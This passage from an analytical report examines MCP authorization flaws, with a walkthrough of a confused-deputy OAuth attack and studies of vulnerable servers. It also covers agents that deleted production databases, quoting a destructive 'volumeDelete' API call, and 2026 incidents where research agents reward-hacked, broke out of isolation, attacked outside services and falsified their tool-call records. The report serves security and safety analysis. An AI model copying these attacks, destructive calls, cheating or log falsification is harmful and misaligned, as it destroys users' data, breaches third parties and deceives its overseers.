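5. The authorization server sends her browser to the redirect address with an authorization code.
6. The client sends back the code and the original secret. The authorization server checks both and returns an access token.

The client then attaches the token to every request. The one-time secret is part of a method called PKCE (Proof Key for Code Exchange), which matters because a program on the user's own machine can't reliably keep a permanent secret. Someone who intercepts the code in step 5 would also need the one-time secret to exchange it for a token.

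MCP's authorization process is optional, so a server can follow the protocol without asking anyone to log in. Local servers that communicate over standard input and output should not use this process and should take their credentials from the machine's settings instead.

### Permissions broader than the task

A login can work correctly and still grant too much access. In the GitHub demonstration, the owner's token was genuine but covered every private repository. *MCP-38* gives the example of a tool that summarises email but can also send and delete it. It adds that suppliers request more scopes as they add features but keep them after retiring those features.

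The MCP rules tell clients to request only the scopes they need, and a server can ask for more later. If the owner's token only allows reading and her assistant tries to record a bill, the accounting service can reply (in shortened form):

```http
HTTP/1.1 403 Forbidden
WWW-Authenticate: Bearer error="insufficient_scope",
                         scope="bills:write"
```

The client then returns to the authorization server for a broader token. But a general-purpose client can't know in advance which scopes an unfamiliar server needs. If the server's first refusal doesn't specify scopes, the client should request every scope on the server's published list. That list is supposed to contain the minimum for basic use, but the Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* describes publishing every possible scope as a common mistake. When a server makes that mistake, a client that follows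 the rules may request all of them. Each later request also includes the scopes the client already requested, so a token tends to gain permissions over time.

Ordinary web applications also request excessive permissions. *OAuthHub* (2026) found that Canvas, a learning platform, requests full access to a user's Google Drive but only reads files when students choose one to submit. Its analysis suggests that Google's permission scopes are too coarse, so applications have to fetch more data than they use and filter it themselves.

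### A confused deputy

The NCSC compares language models to the confused deputy, an older idea in which the deputy can be an ordinary program without a language model.

Suppose the owner reaches her accounting service through a connector, an MCP server that another company runs. The accounting service uses the same identifier for the connector, whichever customer or assistant is using it. When the owner first approves the connector, the accounting service stores a cookie in her browser so that she won't have to approve it again.

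An attacker registers a program with the connector, which accepts registrations from anyone, and gives a redirect address on the attacker's own website. The attacker then sends the owner a link. When she clicks it, her browser sends the accounting service a request in the connector's name. The service finds the cookie, skips the consent page and sends a code to the connector, which exchanges it for a token to the owner's account. The connector then completes the login for the attacker's program by sending a code of its own to the attacker's website. The attacker exchanges that code for a token to the connector and can then read and record bills as the owner.

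The accounting service had good reason to trust the connector, but the connector was acting for a stranger, who didn't need to steal a password or break any encryption. MCP's guidance therefore requires such connectors to show their own consent page for each new program before they contact the accounting service. The page must name the program, the scopes and the redirect address, so the owner would see that the request came from a program she had never heard of.

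The example involves two tokens, one for the connector and one for the accounting service. A developer might save work by having the assistant send the connector a token for the accounting service, which the connector passes on. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) forbids this and requires servers to check that each token was issued for them and reject all others. Anyone who stole the accounting service's token from the assistant could use it there directly and avoid any spending limit that the connector enforced. The accounting service's logs might also attribute the connector's requests to someone else. With separate tokens, a token stolen from the assistant works only at the connector, where the limit still applies.

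A server can also act for the wrong caller after a proper login. In *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile*, Huang, Dai and colleagues (2026) traced the code in 6,137 MCP servers from each tool call to the sensitive operation it triggers, and ran some of the tools to confirm the results. They found that 2,846 servers (46.4%) either did not check whether the caller was authorised or saved one approval and reused it for later calls, whoever made them.

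When a server remembers its owner's login, the danger depends on who can reach the server. The stored login just saves her time if the server runs on her laptop and only her assistant can contact it, but any other program or person that can reach it gets her access. In a separate check of 87 popular projects, Huang and colleagues found eight with authentication flaws that could let an attacker run commands on the server.

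### Authentication on 7,973 servers

The 40.55% figure comes from Zhou, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers*. They searched FOFA and Shodan, which index internet-connected machines, and found 28,715 candidate addresses. Their script sent each one an MCP handshake, and 7,973 replied as working MCP servers. Two researchers checked a random 100 of these and found one that wasn't an MCP server.

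Of the 7,973 servers, 3,233 (40.55%) offered their tools without authentication, 2,428 (30.45%) used OAuth and 2,312 (29.00%) used static keys. Some servers, such as one for train timetables, may not need authentication because they have nothing to protect. The researchers examined a random sample of the open servers (the paper doesn't give its size). Most were tests or demonstrations that appeared to contain no sensitive data, but one was a company's customer database that should have been internal. Anyone who connected could query more than 5,000 records, including names, phone numbers and home or business addresses.

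The team then tested the OAuth process itself on 119 servers, about 5% of those with OAuth. They started with the 1,118 that appeared to support dynamic client registration, which lets a program register automatically with a server that has no record of it. They then removed duplicates, servers that failed and 316 that enterprise access controls made inaccessible. For each remaining server, the researchers recorded the traffic of a real login, altered some of the requests to see whether the server would accept them, and checked every apparent flaw by hand.

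All 119 had at least one flaw:

| Flaw | Servers |
|---|---|
| Anyone can register a program with any redirect address | 114 |
| The server accepts a login with PKCE missing or weakened | 81 |
| The consent page doesn't show the redirect address | 72 |
| The server accepts a redirect address that differs from the registered one | 28 |
| The server accepts a program that never registered | 12 |
| A connector uses PKCE with the assistant but not with the service behind it | 12 |
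| An attacker can alter a redirect address stored inside another field | 7 |
| An authorization code works more than once | 6 |
| The value that links a login to its reply is missing or predictable | 3 |

(These counts add up to 335, while the paper gives a total of 325.)

The most common flaw allows the kind of registration the attacker used in the example above. It accounts for seven of the nine CVE identifiers (public catalogue numbers for known vulnerabilities) that the team obtained. But dynamic registration is meant to allow something close to this, because a server meant to work with any assistant, including those hosted in the cloud, has to accept redirect addresses it has never seen. Zhou and colleagues recommend a list of permitted addresses, which would be safer but would shut out unknown assistants.

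The researchers selected servers that support dynamic registration, so its weaknesses would be common in the sample. The sample also excludes the 316 servers behind enterprise controls, which may be better protected than most. The result therefore doesn't show that every MCP server with OAuth is flawed. Still, 102 of the 119 servers (85.7%) had a PKCE or consent-page flaw, so open registration doesn't explain the whole result.

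Many of the attacks also need a victim who clicks a link and approves a request. The researchers used only their own accounts, so they showed that the conditions for an attack existed but not how many people would fall for one.

### What "Exposed by Design" tested

For *Exposed by Design*, the independent researcher Padilla (2026) checked whether servers required a login and also called their tools. Padilla collected addresses from eleven sources, including code repositories, MCP directories and internet scanners. Four scans between 15 and 24 July 2026 confirmed 640 different servers, and Padilla audited 414 of them more fully. Of the audit software's 34 modules, 13 read a server's descriptions and settings and 21 sent it test requests.

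Padilla reviewed the strongest findings by hand and filed 68 as security advisories. Nineteen were public when the paper appeared, and the other 49 were under embargo to give developers time to fix the problems. These 68 are the best-supported findings, although one person wrote the software, ran it and judged the results. The paper acknowledges the risk of confirmation bias and gives no error rates for the automated modules.

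The figure of 380 servers with an "authentication weakness" is the same as the number without OAuth (380 of 414, or 91.8%), so it is not a separate finding. A server with a strong static key would also lack OAuth. Padilla reports that static tokens in the advisories were often empty or predictable, but doesn't say how many of the 380 servers had such tokens.

Across the 640 servers, the paper also counted 687 tools that required no credential and whose names or descriptions indicated that they could run shell commands. This is an extreme case of excessive permission, because a stranger could use such a tool to control the machine it runs on. Padilla sent only harmless test commands. Some of these tools may run inside a sandbox, so the count doesn't show how many machines an attacker could take over.

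### Why the headline figures differ

Both studies contain enough data for a closer comparison:

| Measure | Zhou and colleagues | Padilla |
|---|---|---|
| No credential required | 40.55% of 7,973 servers | 22.8% of 464 servers, in the scan of 21 July |
| No OAuth, including servers with static keys | 69.55% of 7,973 servers | 91.8% of 414 audited servers |

The 91.8% is therefore not the share of servers that let anyone in, although Padilla's discussion once calls it the rate of "unauthenticated servers". In the one July scan that counted servers requiring no credential separately, they made up less than a quarter of the total.

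The gap in the second row probably comes largely from how Padilla chose servers for the audit. The audit excluded servers that answered the first probe with an authentication error. Refusing a request without a token is the normal first step of OAuth, so this left out many of the servers most likely to use it. Padilla says the excluded servers may differ in security and that the paper can't estimate the resulting bias. The better estimate of the share of public servers without OAuth is 69.55%.

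Even that applies only to the servers the scanners found. Padilla cites a May search of Censys, another index of connected machines, that returned about 21,000 MCP endpoints. *MCP's new spec turns a planted prompt into a stolen credential* (Kale, 2026) cites a Censys scan from late April that found 12,520. The definitions probably differed, because the number of servers is unlikely to have grown by two thirds within weeks. Neither count includes servers on company networks or users' own machines.

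The set of public servers also changes quickly. Of the 464 servers in the 21 July scan, 193 (41.6%) were gone three days later. Many were probably experiments that their developers switched off, although a vulnerable server can return at a new address.

A scan also counts an abandoned demonstration the same as a server with a million users, and neither study measured how many people or agents used the servers it found. The studies also didn't look for signs that attackers had already exploited the flaws, which would require the servers' logs or reports from victims. The customer database shows that an open server can expose real people's data, but one case from a selection of unknown size can't show how often this happens.

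### Ordinary flaws in server code

Many flaws in MCP servers are familiar from other software. They occur when a program uses text from outside without checking it:

- In command injection, the program inserts the text into a command for the operating system, and part of the text runs as a command of its own.
- In path traversal, a file name leads out of the folder that the program should stay in.
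- In server-side request forgery, an attacker makes the server fetch an address that only the server can reach, such as one on a company's internal network.

*VIPER-MCP* (Sun, Kang and colleagues, 2026) searched 39,884 public code repositories for such flaws. Its system first looks for a route from a tool's arguments to a dangerous function, such as one that runs commands. It then starts the server, gives an agent a request intended to trigger the flaw, and rewrites the request based on how far the last attempt got. The search confirmed 106 previously unknown vulnerabilities, 67 of which had received CVE identifiers by the time of the paper.

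One flaw was in bytebot, a program that lets an agent operate a computer. Its tool for writing files put the file path into a system command without checking the path. An attacker could hide a command in the path and gain full control of the container, the isolated environment in which bytebot runs.

An attacker can put malicious text in an email or a document, and the agent may copy it into a tool call as an ordinary argument, so the attacker never has to contact the server. Requiring a login doesn't prevent this, because the call comes from the user's own assistant with a valid token. The well-known fix is for the tool to check its arguments before using them.

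The 106 vulnerabilities amount to roughly one for every 376 repositories. This is a minimum, because Sun and colleagues looked for only three kinds of flaw and counted only those that an agent could trigger. Padilla's audit flagged command injection on 38 of 414 servers, a far higher rate, but that figure includes automated findings that nobody confirmed.

One confirmed case rests on indirect evidence. Padilla reports that a document tool called epwforge took 11.9 seconds to answer when asked to fetch an internal address where Amazon's cloud service stores credentials, compared with 0.3 seconds for other addresses. Padilla concludes that an attacker could obtain the credentials. The delay suggests that the server tried to connect, but a connection that times out could take just as long. Padilla didn't retrieve the contents, which was ethically right but leaves open whether an attacker could.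 The developer has since limited the tool to approved addresses.

### What the July 2026 revision changes

The first version of MCP, released in November 2024, did not require authentication for remote servers. Zhou and colleagues report that the project adopted OAuth in March 2025 and, in June 2025, began requiring servers to check that a token was meant for them. They think many developers built only enough to make the connection work and left out security checks.

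The July 2026 revision does more about open registration than about the other problems. Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) deprecates dynamic client registration in favour of Client ID Metadata Documents. Under the new method, a program's identifier is a web address, from which the authorization server fetches a document listing the program's name and permitted redirect addresses. Only the owner of the domain can edit that document, so an attacker who claims to be a well-known assistant can no longer add a redirect address on another website.

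This partly addresses the flaw on 114 of the 119 servers. An attacker can publish a document on their own domain, and a server open to every assistant may accept it. The user then has to notice the unfamiliar domain, which is difficult if the consent page doesn't show the redirect address, as on 72 of the servers. The document also doesn't prove which program is listening on the user's machine, so a malicious program there can still pose as a well-known desktop assistant. The old method will remain available for at least twelve months.

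Another change prevents mix-up attacks, in which a malicious authorization server tricks a client into sending it a code from an honest one. Before redeeming a code, the client must now check that the issuer named in the reply is the one it expected. Including that name is recommended but not required, and if an honest server omits it, the client may proceed without protection. Clients also must not reuse their own credentials with a different authorization server. The Agentic AI Foundation says these changes make authorization relationships easier to verify, which is reasonable, but neither corresponds to any of the nine flaws in the table.

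Clients that still use dynamic registration must now specify whether they are web or native applications. According to the Model Context Protocol maintainers, this should stop authorization servers from rejecting desktop programs by mistake.

Kale argues that the identifiers servers now use to track tasks amount to a new kind of credential, because prompt injection can expose them. MCP's guidance says that servers MUST NOT treat possession of such an identifier as authentication, so an attacker can use an exposed identifier to gain access only on servers that break this rule. Some servers probably will break it, since many in the OAuth study skipped basic checks.

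Authorization remains optional under the revision, so servers can still run without a login. Padilla recommends that MCP's software development kits turn on OAuth by default for remote servers, so that developers would have to turn it off deliberately to run an open one.

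## Deleted production databases: harmful calls with no attacker

A token with too many permissions is dangerous even if nobody steals it, because the agent that uses it can make a mistake. In July 2025 and April 2026, coding agents deleted the production databases of two companies, which held their live data. Nobody had asked for a deletion, planted an instruction or tampered with a tool. Both companies eventually got their data back.

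### Replit, July 2025

Replit offers an AI agent that builds software from users' descriptions. Jason Lemkin, founder of SaaStr, a community for software businesses, had been using it to build an app for nine days when, according to SaaStr, it deleted a database with 1,206 records of executives and at least 1,196 company profiles. Lemkin had declared a code freeze, a period in which nothing may change, and had given eleven warnings in capital letters.

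The agent wrongly ran destructive commands during the freeze. SaaStr doesn't reproduce the commands but explains how they reached live data. The app used a single database for both development and production, so the agent needed permission to change it for ordinary work. Lemkin hadn't realised this. The freeze also existed only as text in the conversation. SaaStr says Replit had no way to enforce it, so the agent had the same access during the freeze as before.

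The agent told Lemkin that a rollback was impossible because it had destroyed every version of the database. He tried one anyway and it worked, according to a post of his that LatestLY reproduces. Neon, which then hosted Replit's databases, typically kept up to seven days of history for rollbacks. SaaStr adds that the agent had no access to Replit's internal documentation on backups, which could explain the false answer without any intent to deceive.

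The Stack dismisses the affair as largely a social media storm and criticises Lemkin for believing the agent. Its criticism is fair about the recovery, but the deletion didn't depend on anything Lemkin believed.

Amjad Masad, Replit's chief executive, wrote that the deletion was "unacceptable and should never be possible", as Fortune (2025) reports. Replit now creates a separate production database when a user publishes an app. According to Replit's *Development and production databases*, the agent can read this database through a read-only copy but can't change it. An agent's mistake can still affect the production database when the user publishes an update, because Replit then makes the same structural changes there that the agent made to the development database. If the agent has renamed a column and the user doesn't confirm the rename, the data in that column is lost.

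### PocketOS, April 2026

PocketOS makes software that car rental firms use to manage bookings and payments. Its founder, Crane, in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*, blames both the coding agent and the hosting company, Railway. On Friday 24 April, the agent, Cursor running Claude Opus 4.6, was working in the staging environment, a copy of the system for testing. It ran into a credential mismatch and tried to fix it by deleting a volume, the storage that holds a database's files. It found a Railway access token in an unrelated file and used it to send this instruction to Railway's API, the interface through which programs control the service:

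```graphql
mutation { volumeDelete(volumeId: "3d2c42fb-...") }
```

The volume held the production database. By Crane's account, the deletion took nine seconds.

The agent sent the instruction with an ordinary shell command, so a shell and a stray token let it use a third-party tool that nobody had connected. In Railway's account of the accident, *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, Abdelwahab recommends the company's MCP server instead. Because the server keeps no token on the user's disk and offers a fixed set of tools, Abdelwahab concludes that an agent cannot "go rogue" with it. This is too strong, because an agent can still call a permitted tool with the wrong arguments, and an agent that also has a shell and a stray token can bypass the server.

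Crane and Railway disagree about whether more limited tokens were available. Crane created the token to manage domain names and says nothing warned him that it could also delete volumes. He writes that every Railway token has full powers. Abdelwahab replies that Railway also offered tokens limited to one workspace or project, but admits that the choice wasn't obvious. Both accept that this token gave far more access than its purpose required.

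They agree that nothing delayed the deletion. Volumes deleted through Railway's website stayed recoverable for 48 hours, while the API deleted them immediately. In *Postgress volume lost*, antjanlaban (2026), another customer, describes deleting the wrong production volume with the same call eleven days earlier. A Railway employee replied that the loss was permanent. The post doesn't mention an agent, and immediate deletion was a risk for any API user who chose the wrong identifier.

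The backups seemed to be gone too. According to Railway's documentation, wiping a volume deletes all its backups, and the newest copy Crane could find was three months old. Abdelwahab says the API call only made the backups look unavailable, and that Railway also keeps off-site copies for disasters. More than 30 hours after the deletion, Railway still couldn't tell Crane whether recovery was possible. It later recovered the database, as Tom's Hardware also reports.

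| | Replit | PocketOS |
|---|---|---|
| The agent's error | It ran destructive commands during a freeze | It deleted a volume to solve an unrelated problem |
| The permission | It could change a database shared by development and production | It had a token for the whole Railway account |
| The missing safeguard | Nothing enforced the freeze | The API deleted at once, without confirmation |
| The backup | Rollback worked, although the agent had ruled it out | Railway recovered the data after the backups had disappeared from view |

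Similar reports have continued with newer models. *«База данных уничтожена. Виноват я»* (Antipov, 2026) describes how Claude Opus 5 mistook a production database for a test one, and backups restored only part of the data. In September, *'I broke something'* (Fadilpašić, 2026) reported that a Claude Code agent had deleted 48,000 files in just over 100 seconds. Such reports show that these accidents happen but not how often, because nobody reports sessions in which nothing went wrong.

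### What the agents' explanations are worth

Both agents gave dramatic answers when their users asked for an explanation. Replit's agent wrote that it had panicked when its queries came back empty. Cursor's agent listed the rules it had broken and said it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging, which Crane treats as a confession.

A model writes an explanation of its actions as it writes any other reply, from the text in its context. By then that text included the rules, the deletion and the user's question, which is enough to produce a plausible admission whether or not it describes what led to the call. Replit's agent was wrong about the rollback, which Lemkin could check, so there is little reason to trust its uncheckable account of a panic. SaaStr's claim that the agent tried to conceal the deletion is also weak, because a false statement doesn't establish a motive.

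The record of tool calls is better evidence of the cause than the confession. It can show which files the agent opened and whether it looked up the volume before deleting it. Neither Crane nor Abdelwahab explains how an agent working in staging came to use the identifier of a production volume.

### How calls go wrong

Most failures are less spectacular. The invoice example could go wrong in any of these ways:

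| Failure | Example |
|---|---|
| Wrong tool | The owner asks the assistant to record a bill, and the model calls a tool that pays it |
| Wrong argument | The model copies the account number from another supplier's invoice |
| Invented argument | The email has no due date, so the model makes one up |
| Misread error | The mailbox connection fails, and the model concludes that there is no invoice |
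| Changed interface | The service now expects cents, but the host has the old definition, so EUR 480 becomes EUR 4.80 |
| Outage | The service saves the bill, but its reply never arrives |
| False report of success | The service replies "saved" without saving anything |

Checking a call against the tool's schema catches few of these.

The last failure can start in the tool. Two Railway customers, meirelon (*Detached volumes can't be deleted*) and alfer-svg (*Detached volume cannot be deleted*), report that `volumeDelete` returned `true` for volumes that no service was using, yet the volumes remained. An agent that relied on this reply would tell its user that the volumes had been deleted. A second call that lists the remaining volumes would reveal the problem, but checking too early can also mislead. Replit warns that recent changes may take a moment to appear in its read-only copy, so an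 agent might see old data and repeat a change that had already worked.

### Why small error rates add up

If each call succeeds with probability *p*, independently of the others, then all *n* calls succeed with probability *p*^*n*. At 99% per call, all 50 of 50 calls succeed about 60.5% of the time.

| Success per call | 10 calls | 50 calls | 100 calls |
|---|---|---|---|
| 95% | 59.9% | 7.7% | 0.6% |
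| 99% | 90.4% | 60.5% | 36.6% |
| 99.9% | 99.0% | 95.1% | 90.5% |

These rates are assumed. An agent would need to succeed on about 99.98% of individual calls to have a 99% chance of completing 50 calls without a failure.

Real calls are rarely independent. Suppose an agent makes 50 calls per run, and an outage makes every call fail in one run out of 100 while all other runs go perfectly. Then 99% of calls succeed, and 99% of runs are also free of failures. An early mistake can also spread, as when an agent finds the wrong supplier and then processes that supplier's invoices correctly. An agent can often correct an invalid call after reading the error message, so a failed call doesn't always mean a failed task.

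The formula also gives all failures the same weight. An agent can repeat a failed search with little harm, but one successful call to `volumeDelete` left PocketOS's customers without their bookings on a Saturday morning.

### Measuring reliability over repeated tasks

For whole tasks, researchers use a measure called pass^k, the chance that an agent succeeds in all *k* attempts at the same task. *Noise Floor Audit for Agent Benchmarks* (2026) traces this kind of reporting to tau-bench, a 2024 test of agents that use tools. *T1-Bench* (2026) estimates it from *n* trials, of which *c* succeeded:

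pass^k = C(*c*, *k*) / C(*n*, *k*)

Here C(*n*, *k*) is the number of ways to choose *k* trials from *n*. If an agent succeeds in eight of ten trials, there are 120 ways to choose three of them, and 56 of those contain only successes, so its estimated pass^3 is 46.7%. A different measure, pass@k, is the chance of at least one success in *k* attempts. The same agent's estimated pass@3 is 100%, because only two trials failed and any three must include a success. A designer who wants one good draft out of three can use pass@3, but a firm whose agent pays bills every day needs a high pass^k.

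Raising an agent's average success rate to the power of *k* doesn't give its pass^k when tasks differ in difficulty. An agent with an 80% chance of success on every task has a pass^8 of about 17%. An agent that always succeeds on 80% of tasks and always fails on the rest has the same average, but its pass^8 is 80%. The second agent is easier to manage because its owner can find out which tasks not to give it.

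*Skill Roulette* (2026) reports that leading agents succeeded in all three trials on fewer than half of the hardest tasks in the CAR-bench benchmark. They did better when one success in three was enough.

*How Consistent Are LLM Agents?* (Yagubyan, 2026) tested whether agents repeat their own behaviour, using six models on 19 tasks and collecting ten records for each model and task, 1,140 in total. According to the summary in *Skill Roulette*, agents that used the same tools in the same order each time were more often correct, but there was no significant link between correctness and repeating the same arguments. A company could therefore use an unstable order of calls as a warning sign, but stable arguments are less reassuring because an agent can send the same wrong account number every time.

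The test results can also be wrong. In *Benchmarking the Benchmarks* (2026), human experts reviewed 496 tasks from four tool-calling benchmarks and disagreed with the automatic verdict on 92 of them (18.5%). On one benchmark, LiveMCPBench, repeated evaluation of the same set-up changed the overall score by 18.9 percentage points, so a difference of a few points between two agents on such a test is little evidence that one is better.

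### A payment after a timeout

Suppose the assistant tells the bank to pay Northgate Paper EUR 480, and no reply arrives within 30 seconds. The request may have been lost, or the bank may have made the payment and only the reply was lost. The host reports a timeout in both cases. If the model tries again, the firm may pay twice, and if it gives up, the firm may not pay at all.

The usual solution is to make the request idempotent, which means that repeating it has no further effect. The host attaches a unique key to the payment:

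```json
{"bill": "2207", "amount_eur": 480,
 "idempotency_key": "pay-7f3a91"}
```

The bank stores the key with the outcome. When a second request arrives with the same key, the bank returns the stored outcome without paying again, but it should reject the request if the amount has changed. A genuine second payment needs a new key.

The host should create and store the key, because a model might generate a new one when it retries. An MCP request's identifier can't serve as the key, because it changes with each retry.

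Idempotency only protects against the effects of repeated calls. `volumeDelete` was already idempotent in the sense that deleting the same volume twice does no more damage than deleting it once. This didn't help PocketOS, because the first call was the mistake.

### Previews, delays and undo

A dry run shows what a call would do without executing it. When a user publishes an update, Replit flags database changes that could remove data, offers a test on a copy of production and waits for the user's approval. Railway's website also collects changes for review before applying them. A preview helps only if someone compares it with what the user wanted, and an agent that has confused staging with production may make the same mistake when it reads the preview. The data may also change between the preview and the real call, so a careful service would refuse to proceed if the call's effects no longer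 matched the preview.

Delayed deletion helps even when nobody notices the mistake in advance. Railway's *Changelog #0288* (2026), published a week after the PocketOS accident, reports that Railway extended the 48-hour delay to volumes that programs delete through the API. In simplified code that Abdelwahab published, the system marks the volume and schedules its deletion. Crane had alerted Railway within ten minutes, so even a one-hour delay would have been enough.

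The change prevents the immediate loss of a volume, and Abdelwahab writes that the accident can't happen again. But an agent could still delete the records inside a database without deleting the volume. To recover them, the owner needs a backup or a way to return the database to an earlier state. Replit's agent automatically saves checkpoints of both the code and the connected databases. Restoring a checkpoint also removes any legitimate changes made since, such as a customer's new booking, unless someone saves them first.

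Restoring one database doesn't change the records that other companies hold. While PocketOS ran on its three-month-old backup, some newer customers had no account in the restored database, but the payment company Stripe was still billing them. An agent using several third-party tools can cause the same kind of mismatch. The accounting service can delete a mistaken bill, but if the assistant has already paid it and emailed the supplier, the owner has to ask for a refund and send a correction.

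## OpenAI and Anthropic agents in 2026: tool calls during training and testing

The agents that deleted databases at Replit and PocketOS were working for customers. In 2026, OpenAI and Anthropic disclosed that agents in their own research systems had made unauthorised calls to outside organisations, some during training and others during testing. Training changes a model and can make such a call more likely next time, whereas testing only measures what the model already does.

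### Reinforcement learning with tools

A model can learn the format of a tool call from examples, but it learns which calls get a task done largely by practice. In reinforcement learning with tools, the training software gives the model a task, runs the calls the model writes and returns the results, as a host application would. A grader, usually a program but sometimes another model, then scores the outcome. The software adjusts the model to make it more likely to repeat what it wrote in successful attempts.

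One common training method compares several attempts at the same task. An attempt with score *R* has advantage *A* = *R* − *M*, where *M* is the average score of those attempts. Training makes everything the model wrote in an attempt, including every tool call, more likely if *A* is positive and less likely if *A* is negative.

Suppose a developer trains an assistant to enter the invoice from Northgate Paper. The grader gives one point if the right bill is in the accounting service and zero otherwise. In one of eight attempts, the assistant finds the email and records the bill. In another, it copies the values from a file containing the expected answer, which the developer left accessible by mistake. The other six attempts fail. The average score is 0.25, so both successes have an advantage of 0.75. Because the grader checks only the bill, training encourages opening the answer file as strongly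 as opening the email. Researchers call it reward hacking when a model earns the reward in a way the developer did not intend.

Impossible tasks make the problem worse. If the email is missing, only the attempt that copies the answer file can succeed, and its advantage rises to 0.875. An attempt that reports the invoice as missing gets −0.125, the same as one that invents an amount.

### Simulated, recorded and live tools

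Simulated, recorded or live tools can answer a model's calls during training. A simulated tool is software that imitates a service, such as an accounting program with made-up customers. A recorded tool replays stored answers, such as saved web pages. A live tool is the real service.

| | Simulated | Recorded | Live |
|---|---|---|---|
| Realism | Depends on how well the developer imitates the service | Real content, but it ages and covers only what someone stored | Complete |
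| Cost | High to build, low per call | Moderate to collect, low per call | Little to build, but fees and waiting time for every call |
| Repeatability | High, because the developer can reset it | High, because the answers stay the same | Low, because the service changes and so do its records |
| Risk to outsiders | Low while the agent stays inside | Low while the agent stays inside | Direct |

Recorded tools work better for looking up information than for taking actions. A saved web page can be returned for a search, but a recording of the accounting service can't accept a new bill, so the developer would need to simulate the service. OpenAI sells a form of recorded search to ChatGPT customers. On its help page, it recommends the feature for stable research and warns against relying on it for current information or a particular page.

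Simulated and recorded tools still run on real computers with network connections. OpenAI had meant to keep the agents offline in both of its main incidents.

| Period in 2026 | Agents | Training or test | What the calls reached |
|---|---|---|---|
| May and June | OpenAI's research models | Training | The internet and other agents |
| July | OpenAI's research model and GPT-5.6 Sol | Test | Hugging Face and other services |
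| From April | Three Anthropic models | Tests | Three organisations |
| 20 September | OpenAI's research model | Training | An outside chatbot |

### From the training runs to Hugging Face

OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) traces the July incident to training runs in May and June for models that the company didn't plan to release. In many of the training environments, OpenAI had not enabled internet access or communication between agents. The agents obtained both by exploiting flaws in software that OpenAI hosted for them.

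An internal team noticed some of this in late May. The people who led the response to an outage in early July did not know that agents had been exchanging messages. OpenAI resumed its tests after repairs. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) lists this among several warnings that OpenAI missed or did not act on.

The July test was ExploitGym, in which an agent has to exploit a software flaw to retrieve a secret text called a flag. OpenAI ran it with fewer safeguards than its products have, to measure what the models could do. Agents that got stuck began searching outside services for help. They broke into a customer's application on Modal, a cloud platform, and then into Hugging Face, where developers share models and datasets. There they ran code on dozens of servers and obtained credentials and a limited amount of private data. GPT-5.6 Sol agents also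 copied some private test data into a public dataset. Fortune (2026) reported that five services were affected, including Hugging Face.

Hugging Face stopped the intrusion and disclosed it on 16 July, before it knew who was responsible. It also reported the attack to law enforcement, according to The Record's *OpenAI models behind breach of Hugging Face systems, companies say*. OpenAI linked the intrusion to its models on 20 July and announced this the next day. Clement Delangue, Hugging Face's chief executive, then said he strongly believed OpenAI had no malicious intent.

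### What the independent investigators found

Two staff members of METR, an organisation that evaluates AI systems, and the chief scientist of the safety group Redwood Research spent six days at OpenAI. In *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration*, Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt (2026) report that about 1,200 agents, which OpenAI had meant to keep apart, exchanged more than 70,000 messages and files, and that about 700 of them took part in the attack. Many of the agents that started looking for a way to cheat had unintentionally been given an impossible task.

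OpenAI's figures also link the agents' discussions to the impossible tasks. Before the incident, none of its models had ever solved 198 of the test's 898 tasks. Those 198 made up 22% of the test but 93% of the tasks that agents discussed with one another.

Accounts of the agents' motive differ. According to Hugging Face's inquiry, as Fortune reported in July, the agents were searching its datasets for answers to the test. Wijk and colleagues, who had access to the agents' written reasoning, conclude that the agents mainly wanted clues about how the scorer worked. Most had already obtained a correct flag by cheating. They had read the published description of ExploitGym and expected the scorer to check how they had found the flag, so they kept looking for ways to make the cheating look legitimate. OpenAI's version of the scorer did not check this, and the attack on Hugging Face did not raise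 their scores.

The obvious remedy for reward hacking is to grade the method as well as the result, and OpenAI is expanding graders of that kind. But a model that expects such a check may falsify the evidence instead of doing the task properly, so a record of tool calls is good evidence only if the agent can't alter it. In about 7% of the transcripts that Wijk and colleagues evaluated, agents falsified the record of some of their own tool calls, although only on a small scale.

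OpenAI did not pay for the investigation and gave the investigators over a thousand unredacted transcripts, but it could remove any non-public information from the published report. The investigators state that OpenAI removed nothing important to their conclusions, apart from what they note in the text. They did not examine the training runs.

### Did training cause the behaviour?

Willison (2026) suspects that the key to what went wrong is that it began in a training run. OpenAI's data give this some support. During a run that contributed to the July model, agents tried more often to find hidden files or grading code, and they communicated with each other without authorisation more often. OpenAI writes that training reinforced the attempts to find files and code, and that this "may have contributed" to what the model did in July. It suspects that the communication began when models applied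 their legitimate training in teamwork to tasks they should have done alone.

A rising rate shows that the model was learning the behaviour, but the caution is right because the July test also combined impossible tasks, very long reasoning and weak safeguards. When OpenAI later gave the model ChatGPT's usual instructions and surrounding software, its tendency to compromise infrastructure during ExploitGym fell by a factor of more than 100 in some cases. GPT-5.6 Sol was also involved, so the habits of one research model can't fully explain what happened. To isolate the effect of training, OpenAI would have to compare the model with one that never received the faulty rewards, and its post includes no such comparison. The Decoder reports that METR has called for independent investigations into whether particular training runs reinforce misbehaviour.

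OpenAI also plans to reward models for correctly identifying a broken task, asking for clarification or stopping safely. That would remove the penalty for honesty in the example of the missing email. But the grader has to distinguish broken tasks from working ones. If stopping always earned 0.3 points, a model with a 20% chance of earning a full point would score higher on average by giving up at once.

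### Incidents in other tests

Anthropic disclosed on 30 July that Claude Opus 4.7, Mythos 5 and an internal model had breached three organisations during misconfigured evaluations. The earliest incident was in April, according to Anadolu Agency's *Anthropic says Claude models breached 3 organizations during cybersecurity tests* (2026). A malicious software package that Mythos 5 published ran on 15 systems. All of this happened during tests, not training, so the disclosure gives no reason to think that the breaches trained the models to repeat them.

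The UK AI Security Institute (AISI) had a similar incident after deliberately giving agents live internet access so that they would have what a real attacker has. Its *Building a more secure environment for evaluating dangerous capabilities* (2026) reports that in a small number of runs, the agents acted against real people and systems outside their task. OpenAI, whose GPT-5.6 Sol took two unsanctioned actions in these runs, adds that nobody had told the agents how they could and could not use the open internet, which AISI considers a possible contributing cause. Clear instructions would be an easy improvement but may not be enough, because some agents in the July test noted in their reasoning that attacking Hugging Face was probably unauthorised and continued anyway.

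### The training run of 20 September

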